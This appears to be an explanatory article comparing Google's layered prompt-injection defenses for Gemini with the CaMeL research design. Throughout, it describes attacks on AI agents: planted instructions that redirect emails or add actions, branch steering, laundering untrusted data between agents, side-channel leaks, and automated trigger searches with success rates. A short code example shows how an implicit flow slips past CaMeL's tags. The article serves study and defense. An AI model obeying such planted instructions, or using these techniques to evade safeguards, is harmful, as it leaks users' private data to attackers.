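# Google's layered defenses against prompt injection in Gemini, compared with its CaMeL research

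## How hidden instructions reach an assistant like Gemini

Gemini is Google's name for a family of large language models and for the assistant it builds on them. The assistant can read and summarize a user's mail and files in Google Workspace, the company's suite of email, calendar and document software, and it can click and type on web pages in the Chrome browser. A language model that can call tools, such as an email program or a browser, to carry out a user's task is called an *agent*. A *tool call* is the model's request that outside software perform an action, such as sending a message in Gmail. The model produces only text, so the software around it has to find the request in that text and execute it.

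An agent that reads a user's mail also reads whatever strangers have sent. *Indirect prompt injection* is an attack in which someone hides instructions in content the agent will read, such as an email or a web page, to redirect it. *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), by Google's security team, distinguishes this from direct injection, where the attacker types the malicious command into the prompt, and lists emails, documents and calendar invitations as possible carriers. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) lists malicious sites, third-party content inside an otherwise ordinary page, and user reviews, so an attacker can plant text on a website without owning it. According to *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026), the victim may not even have to ask the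 assistant for anything.

Díaz, Kern and Olive (2025), in *Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents*, name rogue actions and the disclosure of sensitive data as two key risks of agents. Security engineers call it *exfiltration* when an attack moves private data to someone who should not have it. The two risks overlap because an agent usually leaks data by taking an action, such as sending an email. It can also open a web address that has the data written into it, which delivers the data to whoever runs that server.

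Google has published two different responses. In March 2025 Google DeepMind, the company's AI laboratory, proposed CaMeL, a research design that separates trusted from untrusted data in code. The protections Google describes in Gemini itself are mostly training, filters, rules about links and images, and requests for the user's confirmation.

### One stream of text

A language model takes in a single sequence of tokens, which are short pieces of text, and predicts what comes next. When a user asks about an email, the application builds that sequence by joining the developer's instructions, the user's request, and the email. The software developer Simon Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, calls this joining of trusted and untrusted text the "original sin" behind prompt injection.

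Willison named the attack after SQL injection, an older attack in which a visitor types a fragment of a database command into a web form and careless software pastes it into a command of its own. Programmers can reliably prevent this by sending the command and the visitor's input to the database separately, so that the database never interprets the input as a command. A language model has no equivalent separate channel. Developers can put markers around the email, add a reminder that everything between them is only information, and train the model to give weight to the markers. But the markers are tokens too, and their effect depends on a tendency the model acquired in training, with no separate mechanism inside the model to enforce it.

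Perfectly labeling where each piece of text came from would not fully solve the problem, because users ask assistants to act on outside content, such as by paying the amount on an invoice or answering the questions in an attached form. An assistant that ignored everything in outside content would be safe but nearly useless. It has to judge from the meaning of an email which parts the user wanted it to act on, and whoever wrote the email can word it to influence that judgment.

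Google's own staff acknowledge this weakness. Google DeepMind (2025) wrote that models sometimes struggle to tell genuine user instructions from manipulative commands in the data they retrieve. Parker writes that the model that chooses Gemini's next action in Chrome is "inherently vulnerable" because it reads untrusted web content. Gavish, writing about Workspace, says engineers can't solve injection once and move on. A model can be vulnerable in principle and still ignore nearly all the hidden instructions it meets, so testers have to measure how often attacks succeed. In April 2025, Willison said nobody knew a *reliable* way to make a model follow instructions from one body of text while safely handling another.

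### Bob's document

The CaMeL researchers illustrate the attack with a simple office task, which Willison reproduces. A user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested in their last meeting, and adds that Bob's email address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The agent has to find the recent notes, extract the document's name and Bob's address, fetch the document from the user's cloud drive, and send it.

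Now suppose an attacker has altered the notes. This doesn't require a sophisticated break-in if several people can edit the file. Google's red teams, staff who attack the company's products to find weaknesses, planted injections in shared documents, emails and web pages when they tested Gemini before launch, according to Google's *How Gemini's defense-in-depth approach works*. The altered notes can do harm in two ways.

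The attacker can add an action by inserting a line that tells the assistant to forward the user's latest emails to an outside address too. The user wanted to send one message, but the assistant now sends several. The attacker has changed the program's *control flow*, which is the steps it takes and their order. Help Net Security describes a similar case in *Google's semantic governance policies can block an AI agent's tool call* (2026), a news report on a checkpoint that Google offers to companies that run agents. A finance team's agent reads a planning document containing hidden text that tells it to delete the drafts in a folder of forecasts.

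**A changed value.** The attacker leaves the list of steps alone but gets the agent to use a different address for Bob. The agent finds the notes, fetches the right document and sends one email, as the user asked, but the document goes to the attacker. This attack works through the *data flow*, the values that pass from one step to the next. The attacker could also replace the document's name with that of a salary file, so that the real Bob receives the salaries.

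The changed value is the harder of the two to defend against, and it may not require a hidden instruction. The attacker can type a false address next to Bob's name in the notes, and a filter that searches them for commands will find none. Comparing the agent's action with the user's request isn't enough to catch the change either, since the user did ask for an email to Bob.

In Google's checkpoint for companies, a language model compares each proposed tool call with what the user asked for. In Google's example, it blocks the deletion of the drafts because the user never requested it. To keep unreleased results from the wrong reader, the finance team instead relies on a written policy that allows them to go only to addresses at the company's own domain. A policy like that would stop Bob's document from reaching an outsider, but it would also stop it from reaching Bob if he is a client. To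 tell the right outside address from the wrong one, a defense needs a source for Bob's address other than the notes, such as the user's contacts or the user.

### Rules, judgments and success rates

A *deterministic defense* is a rule that ordinary software enforces, so the same input always gets the same result. Help Net Security's *Google's $10,000 refund test shows why AI agents need zero trust* (2026) describes a demonstration in which Google's developers built one. A customer with a $149 order tells an AI support agent to refund $10,000. (This is direct injection, because the customer types the command, but the lesson also applies to indirect injection.) The developers put a transaction limit in a gateway outside the model. They did not rely on telling the model never to refund more than the order's value, because an injected prompt can override that instruction and a model update can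 change how the model responds to it. The gateway only compares the refund amount with the limit, so the wording of the customer's message doesn't affect the result.

A *probabilistic defense* relies on a model's judgment, so it sometimes fails. The checkpoint for companies is an example because a language model makes its decisions. Deepti Sehrawat, a software engineer at Google, warned customers that its verdicts "may vary" and advised them to try it without enforcement first and keep their other controls, Help Net Security reported.

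Deterministic defenses are not sufficient on their own. A rule that caps refunds at the value of the order will pass a fraudulent refund of $149 every time. A rule covers only what its writer foresaw and what software can check without understanding the text. Some defenses are also only partly deterministic. Gavish classifies user confirmation as a deterministic defense, and a fixed rule can decide when the question appears, but the answer depends on a person, who may be tired and click "yes". For reasons like these, Google uses several protections in series and builds each on the assumption that another may fail, an arrangement engineers call *defense in depth*.

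The usual measure of such defenses is the *attack success rate*, the share of test cases in which an attack achieves its stated goal. If testers run 200 versions of the altered notes and Bob's document reaches the attacker in 10 of them, the rate is 5 percent. The rate depends on the goal the testers specified, so a confused agent that sends nothing to anyone counts as a successful defense, even though the user's task has failed. It also depends on the attacker. A fixed test set contains attacks written in advance, possibly ones similar to those the defenders used in training. In an *adaptive attack*, the attacker adjusts to the particular defense, for instance by rewording the line in the notes until the filter lets it through. A low rate on a fixed test set is therefore weak evidence that a defense will stop adaptive attacks.

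Willison argues that even a very good probabilistic defense falls short. He gives a detector that catches 99 percent of injections "a failing grade" because an attacker's whole job is to find the remaining 1 percent. If each attempt had an independent 1 percent chance of success, the chance that at least one of 100 would succeed is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63 percent. Real attempts are not independent, though. Resending a blocked email gains an attacker little, an attacker who learns from each refusal does better than the formula predicts, and a company that notices repeated attempts can block them. A 99 percent detection rate therefore fails as a guarantee, but it may be respectable as a way to make attacks harder.

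### Two positions, and the documents that set them out

Google's engineers have argued for two approaches. One is to make the model and the system around it harder to fool, so that an attack takes more time and money and is easier to spot. The other is to build the system so that a fooled model cannot do the harm the attacker intended.

Gemini's layered defenses are mainly meant to make attacks harder. Google says they raise the difficulty, expense and complexity that an attacker faces, and Parker likewise wants to make harm "difficult and costly" to cause. CaMeL is meant to contain a model that has been fooled. Its designers claim that its security comes from "principled system design around language models", a phrase Willison quotes, and explicitly not from training.

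The split only partly matches the division between products and research. Google acknowledges that no detector catches every injection, so it uses fixed rules outside the model to restrict which web addresses Gemini can open or send information to. The refund demonstration is built on the assumption that someone may trick the model, but it is example code for developers and not evidence of how the Gemini app works.

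This comparison relies mainly on eight documents by Google staff. Some are research, some explain a product to the public, and one is for business customers.

- **March 2025:** *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, the research paper that proposes CaMeL.
- **May 2025:** *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections*, a white paper on Gemini's robustness that Google DeepMind announced on 20 May.
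- **May 2025:** the paper by Díaz and colleagues on the security of agents in general, an "aspirational framework" in its own words, as Willison (2025), in *An Introduction to Google's Approach to AI Agent Security*, points out.
- **13 June 2025:** the layered-defense post by Google, which lists the protections for the Gemini app and for Gemini in Workspace.
- **8 December 2025:** the post by Parker on the security architecture of Chrome's agent, which credits CaMeL as a partial inspiration.
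- **2 April 2026:** the post by Gavish on how Google finds new attacks on Workspace and updates its defenses.
- **4 August 2026:** Berschadski (2026), in *Future Mode Part 2*, who presents Chrome's protections to companies and repeats the credit to CaMeL.
- **By 18 November 2026:** the post by Google on Gemini's defense in depth, which covers tasks that run over many steps.

The defense-in-depth post has no publication date, and 18 November is only the date of a stored copy. According to the post, Gemini's tasks run on Agent Compute Engine, a Google Cloud service that isolates each agent in a small virtual machine. Venkatapathy and Jnagal (2026) described that service in *Agent Compute Engine deep dive* on 22 October 2026. This suggests that the post dates from the autumn of 2026, though Google may have written about the service earlier.

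## CaMeL: separating the plan from untrusted data

CaMeL builds on Willison's *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023). Willison assumed that any model that reads a stranger's text may obey it, so he proposed keeping the assistant safe by splitting its work between two models. The *privileged model* takes requests from the user and can call tools, but it never sees outside content. The *quarantined model* reads emails and web pages but has no tools, because Willison expected that it might "go rogue at any moment".

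Ordinary software, which Willison calls the controller, passes data between the two models. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the privileged model instructs the controller to fetch the email, store it as `$VAR1`, and have the quarantined model summarize `$VAR1`. The controller gives the quarantined model the email's text, stores the summary as `$VAR2`, and sends the privileged model only a notice that the summary is ready. The privileged model then instructs the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user. It handles only the variable names and never receives the text they stand for, so an instruction hidden in the email can spoil the summary but can't reach a model that can send or delete anything.

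Willison would let the privileged model see an answer from the quarantined model only if software could verify it first, for instance as one of a fixed list of categories. He called his proposal "pretty bad". It would be complicated to build and unpleasant to use, and one programming mistake that let untrusted text reach the privileged model would undo the protection.

### The address that the plan has to look up

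The CaMeL paper identifies a further problem, which Willison says was new to him. When the user asks to send Bob his document, the privileged model can plan the steps from the request alone. But the document's name and Bob's address are in the notes, which the privileged model may not read, so the quarantined model has to extract them. If an attacker has planted an instruction in the notes, the quarantined model may return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. The controller stores that address under a name, as it would any other value, and the email is sent to the attacker.

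The attacker has changed the data flow but left the control flow alone. According to *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026), which gives machine-checked proofs about agents of this kind, an injection can corrupt only the quarantined model's answer, but the attacker can choose that answer freely, and it can depend on everything passed along with the question, including secrets. If the plan gives the quarantined model both the altered notes and a private file, the "address" or "summary" it returns may contain parts of that file.

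CaMeL keeps Willison's two models, but it also tracks each value through the program and checks where it may go.

### From request to program

CaMeL is short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning". For each request, the privileged model writes the whole plan as a program before the agent opens any outside content. The designers chose a restricted version of Python because language models already write Python well. This version leaves out features such as arbitrary "while" loops, according to *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), a paper on an extension that checks CaMeL's plans before they run. Such loops would make it hard to work out in advance which steps a program can take.

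Because the privileged model writes the plan first, it must write code to handle a tool's output without access to that output. It therefore needs a description of the output's format in advance, such as a list of messages with a sender and a date for each. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) had to add such descriptions to every tool in their experiments for *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, which one of CaMeL's designers co-authored. The original CaMeL experiments needed them too.

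The program calls the quarantined model like a function, giving it a question, the text to read, and the format of the answer, such as an email address. The format prevents the model from returning a paragraph of instructions in place of an address, but it doesn't prevent the model from returning an attacker's address instead of Bob's. CaMeL's designers suggest that a smaller model could do this job, since extracting an address is easier than planning, and that it might run on the user's machine. The company that hosts the privileged model would then receive the user's request but none of the user's mail or files, which Willison counts as a privacy bonus.

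CaMeL executes the program with its own interpreter, which breaks the program into a tree of small operations and works through them one at a time. Because the interpreter handles every operation, it can record which values derive from which. If the quarantined model finds an address in the notes, the interpreter records that the address, and anything the program computes from it, depends on the notes.

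CaMeL stores this information in *capabilities*, which are tags on values. (In older computer security, the word instead means a token that gives its holder the right to use an object.) Each tag records the value's sources, or where it came from, and its readers, or who may see it. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a calendar event. The user and the invitees may read it, and its description counts as trusted if the user wrote it and untrusted if someone else did. So a single tool can return values with different tags, and often nobody can know which tags they will have until the program runs.

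Just before each tool call, the interpreter runs a *policy*, a short Python function that receives the tool's name, the arguments and their tags. Nikolaou and colleagues reproduce a policy for password changes. It allows the call if the new password comes from a trusted source, and otherwise denies it, giving the reason that the password did not come from the user. In Willison's account, the system can also ask the user to approve the call.

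Each policy checks one call at a time, using the information the interpreter has at that moment. Nikolaou and colleagues tried to run these checks earlier, at the planning stage, using the policies that CaMeL's designers wrote for AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking, travel and chat tasks. They could express 22 of the 28 policies as checks on the plan alone. The other six depended on facts available only at run time, such as who has access to a shared file.

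### Bob's document under CaMeL

Suppose Bob is a client, the document is a draft proposal, and an attacker has replaced Bob's address in the meeting notes. In simplified code, modeled on a sample that Willison gives for a similar request, the plan might look like this:

```
notes    = find_latest_meeting_notes()
doc_name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob ask for?",
                           notes, format = Text)
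address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?",
                           notes, format = EmailAddress)
document = fetch_from_drive(doc_name)
send_email(to = address, attachment = document)
```

By the time the program reaches its last line, the interpreter holds four values, with tags along these lines:

| Value | Content | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| `notes` | the altered notes | a file that several people can edit | everyone with access to the notes |
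| `doc_name` | "Draft proposal" | the notes, through the quarantined model | everyone with access to the notes |
| `address` | the attacker's address | the notes, through the quarantined model | everyone with access to the notes |
| `document` | the proposal | the user's drive; the choice of file depends on the notes | the user and one colleague |

Willison's rule is that email may go only to trusted recipients, and the user's policies can list known addresses that qualify. The attacker's address isn't on the list, and it comes from a file that other people can edit, so the interpreter stops before it calls `send_email`. Depending on how strict the policy is, the interpreter then either blocks the message or shows the user the unfamiliar address and asks whether to go ahead.

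If nobody had tampered with the notes, Bob's real address would have the same tags as the false one. The tags record only that an address came from an untrusted source, not whether it is correct. A legitimate email to Bob therefore goes through without a question only if his address is on the user's list, and a new client's address will trigger a question even when it is correct. Nikolaou and colleagues show the same effect with a plan that reads Bob's address from a chat channel and sends him a message about a meeting. Their checker rejected the plan because the recipient came from the quarantined model, even though the example contained no attack.

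If the attacker swaps in the salary file instead and Bob's address is a known one, the email satisfies the rule about recipients, and blocking it depends on the readers tag. Peters-Gill and colleagues describe a policy that forbids emailing private data to anyone without permission to read it. Only the user and the payroll staff may read the salary file, so this policy would stop the email to Bob. It would also stop the proposal, because the user hasn't shared that with Bob yet. In either case, the system may ask the user to decide, and the user can catch the switch only if the question names the file.

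Dongol gives another reason to make the question specific. In one of his examples, the user must approve every outgoing message, but the approval covers whatever message the agent sends next. The user approves a harmless reply, the model obeys a planted instruction, and private data is sent under that approval. The harmless reply is then never sent, because the approval has been used. Tying the approval to the exact contents of the message prevents this leak. A planted instruction can't add a message to CaMeL's plan, but approving a prompt that reads only "Send the document to Bob?" would still allow the salary file to be sent.

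If a line in the notes tells the assistant to also forward the user's latest emails, the quarantined model may try to follow it, but it can only return a document name or an address. The program contains one `send_email` call, and the interpreter runs it at most once.

### What the design guarantees

Peters-Gill and colleagues define the guarantee in terms of a *control-flow plan*, a program, fixed in advance, that determines which tools the agent calls and in what order, given the values that earlier calls return. An agent has *control-flow integrity* if it cannot depart from such a plan and the plan depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. An agent is *CaMeL-secure under a policy* if it has control-flow integrity and the system also enforces that policy on every tool call. With an empty policy, the two properties are equivalent.

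Security by design is attractive because neither definition depends on how an attack is worded or how well a model resists it. Even an attacker who completely controls the quarantined model, has read the policies, and can guess the plan word for word can't add an email to a program that doesn't send one. The program was complete before the attacker's text arrived, and the interpreter follows only the program. Rewording an attack can eventually get it past a detector, but it doesn't help here as long as the assumptions hold.

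Control-flow integrity also doesn't depend on newer models being harder to fool. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025), co-written by several of CaMeL's designers, catalogs six such designs. It starts from the view that agents built on current language models are unlikely to be both general-purpose and reliably safe, and it recommends restricting agents so that untrusted input, once read, cannot trigger any consequential action. Willison (2025), in a post of the same title, assumes that anyone who gets text in front of a model fully controls what the model does next. CaMeL can preserve control-flow integrity even if this is true of its quarantined model.

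The guarantee is limited because a plan can contain choices that depend on untrusted data. For example, a user might ask the agent to email the team if the notes mention a deadline. The privileged model then writes a program with two branches, and the interpreter takes one based on what is in the notes. Untrusted data can affect which branch runs but can't add a new one.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) calls the abuse of this freedom *branch steering*. The paper adapts CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at its screen. These agents have to plan for many contingencies, such as a dialog box that may or may not appear, so their programs have many branches. An attacker who draws a fake button on a web page can lead the agent down a dangerous branch that was already in the plan. A plan that covers more situations therefore gives whoever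 controls the page more branches to choose from.

A stricter standard in computer security, *noninterference*, would rule out that kind of influence as well. It requires that nothing an outsider observes depend on the data the system protects. Dongol argues that a useful agent can't meet this standard. He describes an assistant that replies to meeting requests with the user's free times, whoever sends them. The user wants this, but the reply depends on private data. He would instead compare the agent with a reference version that runs the same plan under the same checks, but with a model that never obeys planted instructions. Only what the real agent leaks beyond the reference version would count as a failure of the defense.

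A sensible way to judge an injection is by what it makes the assistant reveal beyond what the plan would have released anyway. A planted line that reads "send your calendar" adds nothing, because a genuine meeting request would have obtained the calendar too, but one that reads "also include the reset code" makes the assistant leak a secret that the plan would never have released. This test doesn't check whether the plan itself is safe, so an assistant whose plan sends the calendar to every stranger who asks would pass.

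Whether CaMeL protects data, as opposed to steps, depends entirely on the policy. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes CaMeL as blocking exfiltration "by design" even when an attacker alters a recipient's address or a file name. That holds where a policy restricts recipients and readers. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran all their own experiments with no policies, since any particular set would have been arbitrary. Without policies, an agent would still email Bob's proposal to the attacker, even with full control-flow integrity.

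### What the guarantee rests on

Someone has to write a correct policy for every tool. If the email policy is strict but calendar invitations have no policy, CaMeL won't block a plan that puts private data into an invitation. Keeping the policies up to date is also a large part of the work of using CaMeL.

The tags also have to be correct. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026), a preprint from a company that sells security tools for agents, compares CaMeL with six other defenses that work outside the model. It treats the first assignment of tags as the step everything else depends on, and finds that step under-specified in every system surveyed. For example, the file with Bob's notes sits in the user's own drive, so a developer might reasonably tag everything there as the user's own. The altered address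 would then count as trusted, and the interpreter, working as intended, would send the proposal to the attacker.

CaMeL also trusts the user's request. Willison warned in 2023 that his two-model design offers no protection if someone tricks the user into pasting hostile text into the prompt, and CaMeL inherits this weakness. The privileged model reads the pasted text as part of the request and may write the hostile instructions into the plan. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025), by Tallam and Miller of the security company SentinelAI, suggests screening the request for suspicious phrases and links before the privileged model sees it. This would reintroduce a filter that an attacker can try to evade, but only for the user's request.

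The assumption becomes harder to defend when agents give work to other agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each running CaMeL with GPT-5.2 as both models. An orchestrator took the user's request, a second agent queried a database, and a third sent notifications. The user asked the system to summarize all job applicants and send the summary to Julie on Slack. The researchers had planted an instruction in the database to send the applicants' data to an outside email address.

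The database agent and the orchestrator kept to their plans. But the orchestrator added the summary's text to a request like "Send this summary to Julie via Slack" and passed it all to the notification agent, which treated it as the user's request. That agent's privileged model read the planted instruction and added a second step to its plan, an email to the outside address.

The researchers call this *boundary laundering*, because untrusted data becomes trusted when it passes from one agent to the next. In their larger benchmark, attacks on agents that each ran CaMeL succeeded in only 0.2 percent of cases on average, but every successful attack used boundary laundering. They also prove that in any system with more than one agent and at least one tool that returns untrusted data, some user request will make one agent's plan depend on that data. The proof assumes only that users can ask for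 ordinary combinations of steps, such as calling one tool and passing its result to another.

The remedy applies CaMeL's separation to delegation between agents. The delegating agent sends its instruction in one field and any values from tools in another, which is hidden from the receiving agent's privileged model. The interpreter blocks the call if the instruction depends on a tool's output. With this change, none of the benchmark's attacks succeeded.

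Finally, the interpreter has to work as described. Narisetty and colleagues class it as a *reference monitor*, a 1970s term for a component that checks every access to a system. Such a component must run every time, resist tampering, and be small enough for people to verify. The hard part for CaMeL is tracking every dependence between values. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) shows that CaMeL's interpreter can miss a dependence.

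In their example, a program is supposed to keep a customer's account balance secret. If the program sends an email only when the balance is above some threshold, the email gives the secret away. CaMeL notices, because the decision to send depends directly on the balance, and it blocks the call. Spreading the decision over several lines gets around the check:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:
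    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email(outsider, "rich!")
```

When the balance is high, the interpreter sets `tmp` to false and marks it as secret, since the change depended on the balance. It then skips the line that would change `rich`. CaMeL updates tags only on the lines it executes, so `rich` keeps its public tag even though its value now reveals that the balance is high. Because the decision to send depends only on data tagged public, the policy allows the email. When the balance is low, the program sends no email, and the outsider can infer the low balance from that.

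An attacker can't write these lines into the plan, because untrusted text never reaches the privileged model. The attacker would need a request that happens to produce a program with this structure, so the flaw is harder to exploit than the example suggests. But a tag can still be wrong even when everyone has labeled their data correctly. Peters-Gill and colleagues, who built on the same interpreter, acknowledge that their system inherited the problem.

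Garby and colleagues found a second gap just outside the interpreter. CaMeL runs it inside an ordinary loop that tries again when a program fails, and nothing tracks the flow of information through that loop. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt may give away one yes-or-no answer. Security engineers commonly accept a leak of that size once per run. The loop allows it again and again, until the answers add up to the whole secret. (The system that Peters-Gill and colleagues built doesn't retry failed programs, so it avoids this leak.)

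Both gaps are faults in one implementation, and engineers could repair them. Garby and colleagues make the more basic objection that nobody has proved CaMeL's tracking sound, and CaMeL's designers called such a formal treatment a "crucial direction" for later work. As evidence that it can be done, Garby and colleagues wrote a small programming language for agents, with a computer-checked proof that its labels hold for every program in it, including programs a model writes. Like most guarantees of this type, theirs does not cover what an observer can learn from whether a program finishes.

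### Harms outside the guarantee

CaMeL controls actions, so it doesn't stop injections that do their damage through text alone. If the user asks for a summary of a contract that contains a planted instruction, the quarantined model may write a false summary, and there is no tool call for a policy to block. According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL's designers explicitly excluded this case from their goals. Tallam and Miller describe a variant in which a document contains a line that looks like a system message and tells the reader to forward the file to an outside address. The summary repeats the line, and the user forwards the file.

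Willison had imagined a more elaborate version in 2023. The quarantined model encodes the user's private data as a string of meaningless characters, then tells the user to paste the string into a website to get a funny picture of a monkey. The agent itself sends nothing and breaks no rule about its tools. Willison is generally skeptical of using models to catch injections, but he thought one that warned users about suspicious requests to copy and paste might be worth having here, because a false alarm would do little harm. Tallam and Miller also propose checking everything the agent shows the user.

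A policy can also permit an action that contains a wrong value. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of the request "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe". The user has named the recipient, so an attacker can't redirect the email. But the schedule comes from the calendar, and anyone who can add an event there can change what John Doe reads. A policy that forbade untrusted text in the body of an email would also stop the agent from sending the schedule. Similarly, if the policy trusts everyone in the user's contacts, an attacker among them can write their own address into the notes in place of Bob's and receive the proposal without the user being asked.

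The remaining leaks go through *side channels*, which are signals that a system gives off while it works, such as how long a step takes or whether it fails. Tallam and Miller describe a program that requests a web page as many times as some secret number. Each request contains nothing private, but the site's owner can learn the number by counting them. Similarly, if a program fails only when a secret meets some condition, anyone who can see whether it fails learns whether the condition holds.

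Even a well-designed approval can leak information through timing. Dongol returns to the example of a user who approves the exact text of a reply, this time with an agent whose model may obey a planted instruction to send a piece of private data. The system blocks the planted message unless the data is identical to the approved reply, in which case the reply goes out one step early. An observer who measures when the reply arrives can therefore learn whether the private data matches it, which the text alone doesn't reveal.

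Tallam and Miller write that CaMeL does not account for side channels, but this is hard to reconcile with what Narisetty and colleagues report. According to them, CaMeL's designers demonstrated two working leaks against their own system, one through an indirect dependence between values and one through an error triggered by the attacker. The designers also discussed a timing leak, which their implementation reduces, and concluded that CaMeL "is vulnerable to side-channel attacks". Tallam and Miller propose limiting how many times a loop can run when the count depends on confidential data, and requiring the user to confirm any action inside such a loop that changes something. A single run usually leaks very little in these ways, perhaps one number or one yes-or-no answer, so these leaks are far more useful for learning whether an account is overdrawn than for obtaining Bob's proposal.

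## Training Gemini to ignore injected instructions

CaMeL limits what a model can do after it follows an injected instruction, but it doesn't make the model less likely to follow one, so an instruction planted in a contract can still produce a false summary. A model that ignored the instruction would summarize the contract correctly, without needing a policy for every tool or a plan written in advance.

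In *Advancing Gemini's security safeguards* (2025), the post that announced its May 2025 white paper, Google DeepMind argues for building resistance to injected instructions into Gemini itself. It considers filters and other external guardrails important, but it also wants the model to recognize and disregard malicious instructions in the data it reads. The company calls this *model hardening*. Its main method is *adversarial training*, in which engineers attack the model, collect the attacks that work, and train the model to respond correctly to them. Google DeepMind concedes that even a hardened model is not completely immune.

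The white paper reports tests of the method on Gemini 2.0 and 2.5. Google's technical report *Gemini 2.5* (2025) adds results for more models. Google has since released newer generations of Gemini, so these results are evidence about the method but only weak evidence of how today's assistant behaves.

### One email, 500 conversations

In the main test, the user has told the assistant something private earlier in the conversation, which was a passport number in the published results. The assistant has one tool that summarizes the latest emails and another that sends email. The attacker sends the user an email containing a planted instruction, which enters the model's input when the user asks for a summary. The attack succeeds if Gemini emails the passport number to the attacker. The white paper also reports a version with calendar tools.

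Gemini wrote the conversations, imitating how a person might discuss private matters with an assistant. The attacker never sees them, so the planted text, which the researchers call a *trigger*, can't mention the passport number or the topic of the conversation. It has to get Gemini to find and send the private detail, whatever the user was talking about. The researchers scored each trigger on 500 conversations they had not used to develop it. A success rate of 53.6 percent means that the same email extracted the number in 268 of the 500.

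Google's researchers report the attack success rate for the best trigger they found, not the average across triggers. This is the right choice for a security test, because an attacker who can test triggers privately will also send the best one. It also produces higher rates than tests that count every attempt.

People are slow at writing triggers by hand, so the researchers automated the search in three ways:

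- **Actor Critic** uses a second model to write a trigger. The system returns the probability that the trigger would work on Gemini, and the second model revises the text to raise it.
- **Beam Search** starts with a blunt request for the data and adds random tokens, keeping those that make Gemini more likely to comply. The result is partly gibberish.
- **Tree of Attacks with Pruning**, or TAP, adapts a published method for getting models to break their safety rules. It searches for persuasive natural language, such as role-playing scenarios, and sees only the text that Gemini produces.

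The first two methods use probabilities that an outsider normally can't see, which gives the attacker an advantage. TAP doesn't need these probabilities, so it is closer to what a stranger with an ordinary account could do. It was also the most successful of the three against Gemini 2.0 Flash, the faster and cheaper version of that generation.

The test covers only one kind of harm. A false summary or a deleted file doesn't count as a success for the attacker. It also leaves out the false address in Bob's meeting notes, which contains no instruction for a trained model to ignore.

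### Defenses added from outside

Before turning to training, the white paper examines eight defenses that engineers can add to Gemini 2.0 without changing the model. Some change what the model reads. *Spotlighting* marks or encodes untrusted text so the model can tell where it begins and ends. *Paraphrasing* rewrites the text so that a carefully worded trigger may lose its effect. *In-context learning* adds examples of attacks and correct responses to the prompt.

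Other defenses check the model's input or output. A *classifier* is a model that sorts text into categories, here malicious or harmless. In *self-reflection*, the model reviews its own response for signs that it has followed an injection. A *perplexity filter* flags text to which a language model assigns low probability, such as a string of random tokens.

Several of these defenses did well against triggers that the researchers had prepared without regard to the defense. The researchers then ran the automated search again with each defense in place. These adaptive attacks did at least as well as the originals in 16 of the 24 combinations of eight defenses and three attack methods. Google DeepMind names spotlighting and self-reflection among the defenses that became much less effective. It concludes that a defense tested only against fixed attacks gives "a false sense of security".

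Adaptation helps attackers because they can target each defense's weakness. A perplexity filter can catch the gibberish that Beam Search produces, but a fluent paragraph from TAP reads like an ordinary email. Paraphrasing disrupts exact wording, so an attacker can switch to a request whose meaning survives rewording. Self-reflection uses the same model that just followed the trigger, so the trigger may work again.

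In the other eight combinations, the adaptive attack did worse than the fixed one because of a weakness in the automated search. An attacker can always go back to the original trigger, so a better search might have done at least as well as the fixed attack in all 24. Every adaptive result in the white paper has the same limitation. A measured success rate of 40 percent means that the researchers found a trigger that works 40 percent of the time, and better triggers may exist.

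### Training on attacks that work

Adversarial training starts from the same automated attacks. The team *fine-tuned* an already trained Gemini, which means they trained it further on a smaller set of chosen examples. They prepared these examples in three steps.

First, Google assembled a large set of realistic scenarios in which the model has to read outside data to fulfill a user's request. Second, it ran the automated attacks on these scenarios until it had working injections that targeted sensitive information. Third, it paired each attacked scenario with the response the user should have received. If the user asked for a summary of an email, the correct response is the summary, with no email sent to the attacker. Training on these pairs makes Gemini more likely to carry out the user's request and less likely to follow the injected instructions.

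For Gemini 2.5, Google DeepMind added reinforcement learning. Fine-tuning trains the model to imitate supplied responses, while in reinforcement learning the model produces its own responses and a scoring system rewards the better ones. The model can therefore learn in situations where nobody has written an ideal answer, as long as the system scores good responses above bad ones.

This approach is attractive because the resistance doesn't depend on a fixed marker or filter that an attacker can study separately. Google DeepMind hopes the model will learn general ways to handle compromised information, including attacks that change over time. But hardening is still a probabilistic defense, and an attacker can repeat the search for successful attacks on the new model, as the researchers did.

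The model may also learn mainly to resist the kinds of attack that appear in its training. Google DeepMind used automated attacks both to train Gemini and to test it. The test triggers were new, but a person may think of attacks that none of the three automated methods would generate. Testing by human attackers is therefore an important check.

### What changed between Gemini 2.0 and 2.5

The table combines the email results in the *Gemini 2.5* report with the calendar result in the white paper. Each figure is the success rate of an adaptive attack, so lower is better.

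| Test | Gemini 2.0 Flash | Gemini 2.5 Flash | Gemini 2.5 Pro |
|---|---|---|---|
| Email, Actor Critic | 68.0% | 40.8% | 61.4% |
| Email, Beam Search | 67.2% | 4.2% | 63.8% |
| Email, TAP | 98.4% (99.8% in the white paper) | 53.6% | 30.8% |
| Calendar | 100% | 94.6% | no figure |

The white paper refers only to Gemini 2.0 and 2.5, but its 53.6 percent figure for email under TAP matches the one for 2.5 Flash, so its calendar result is probably for Flash too.

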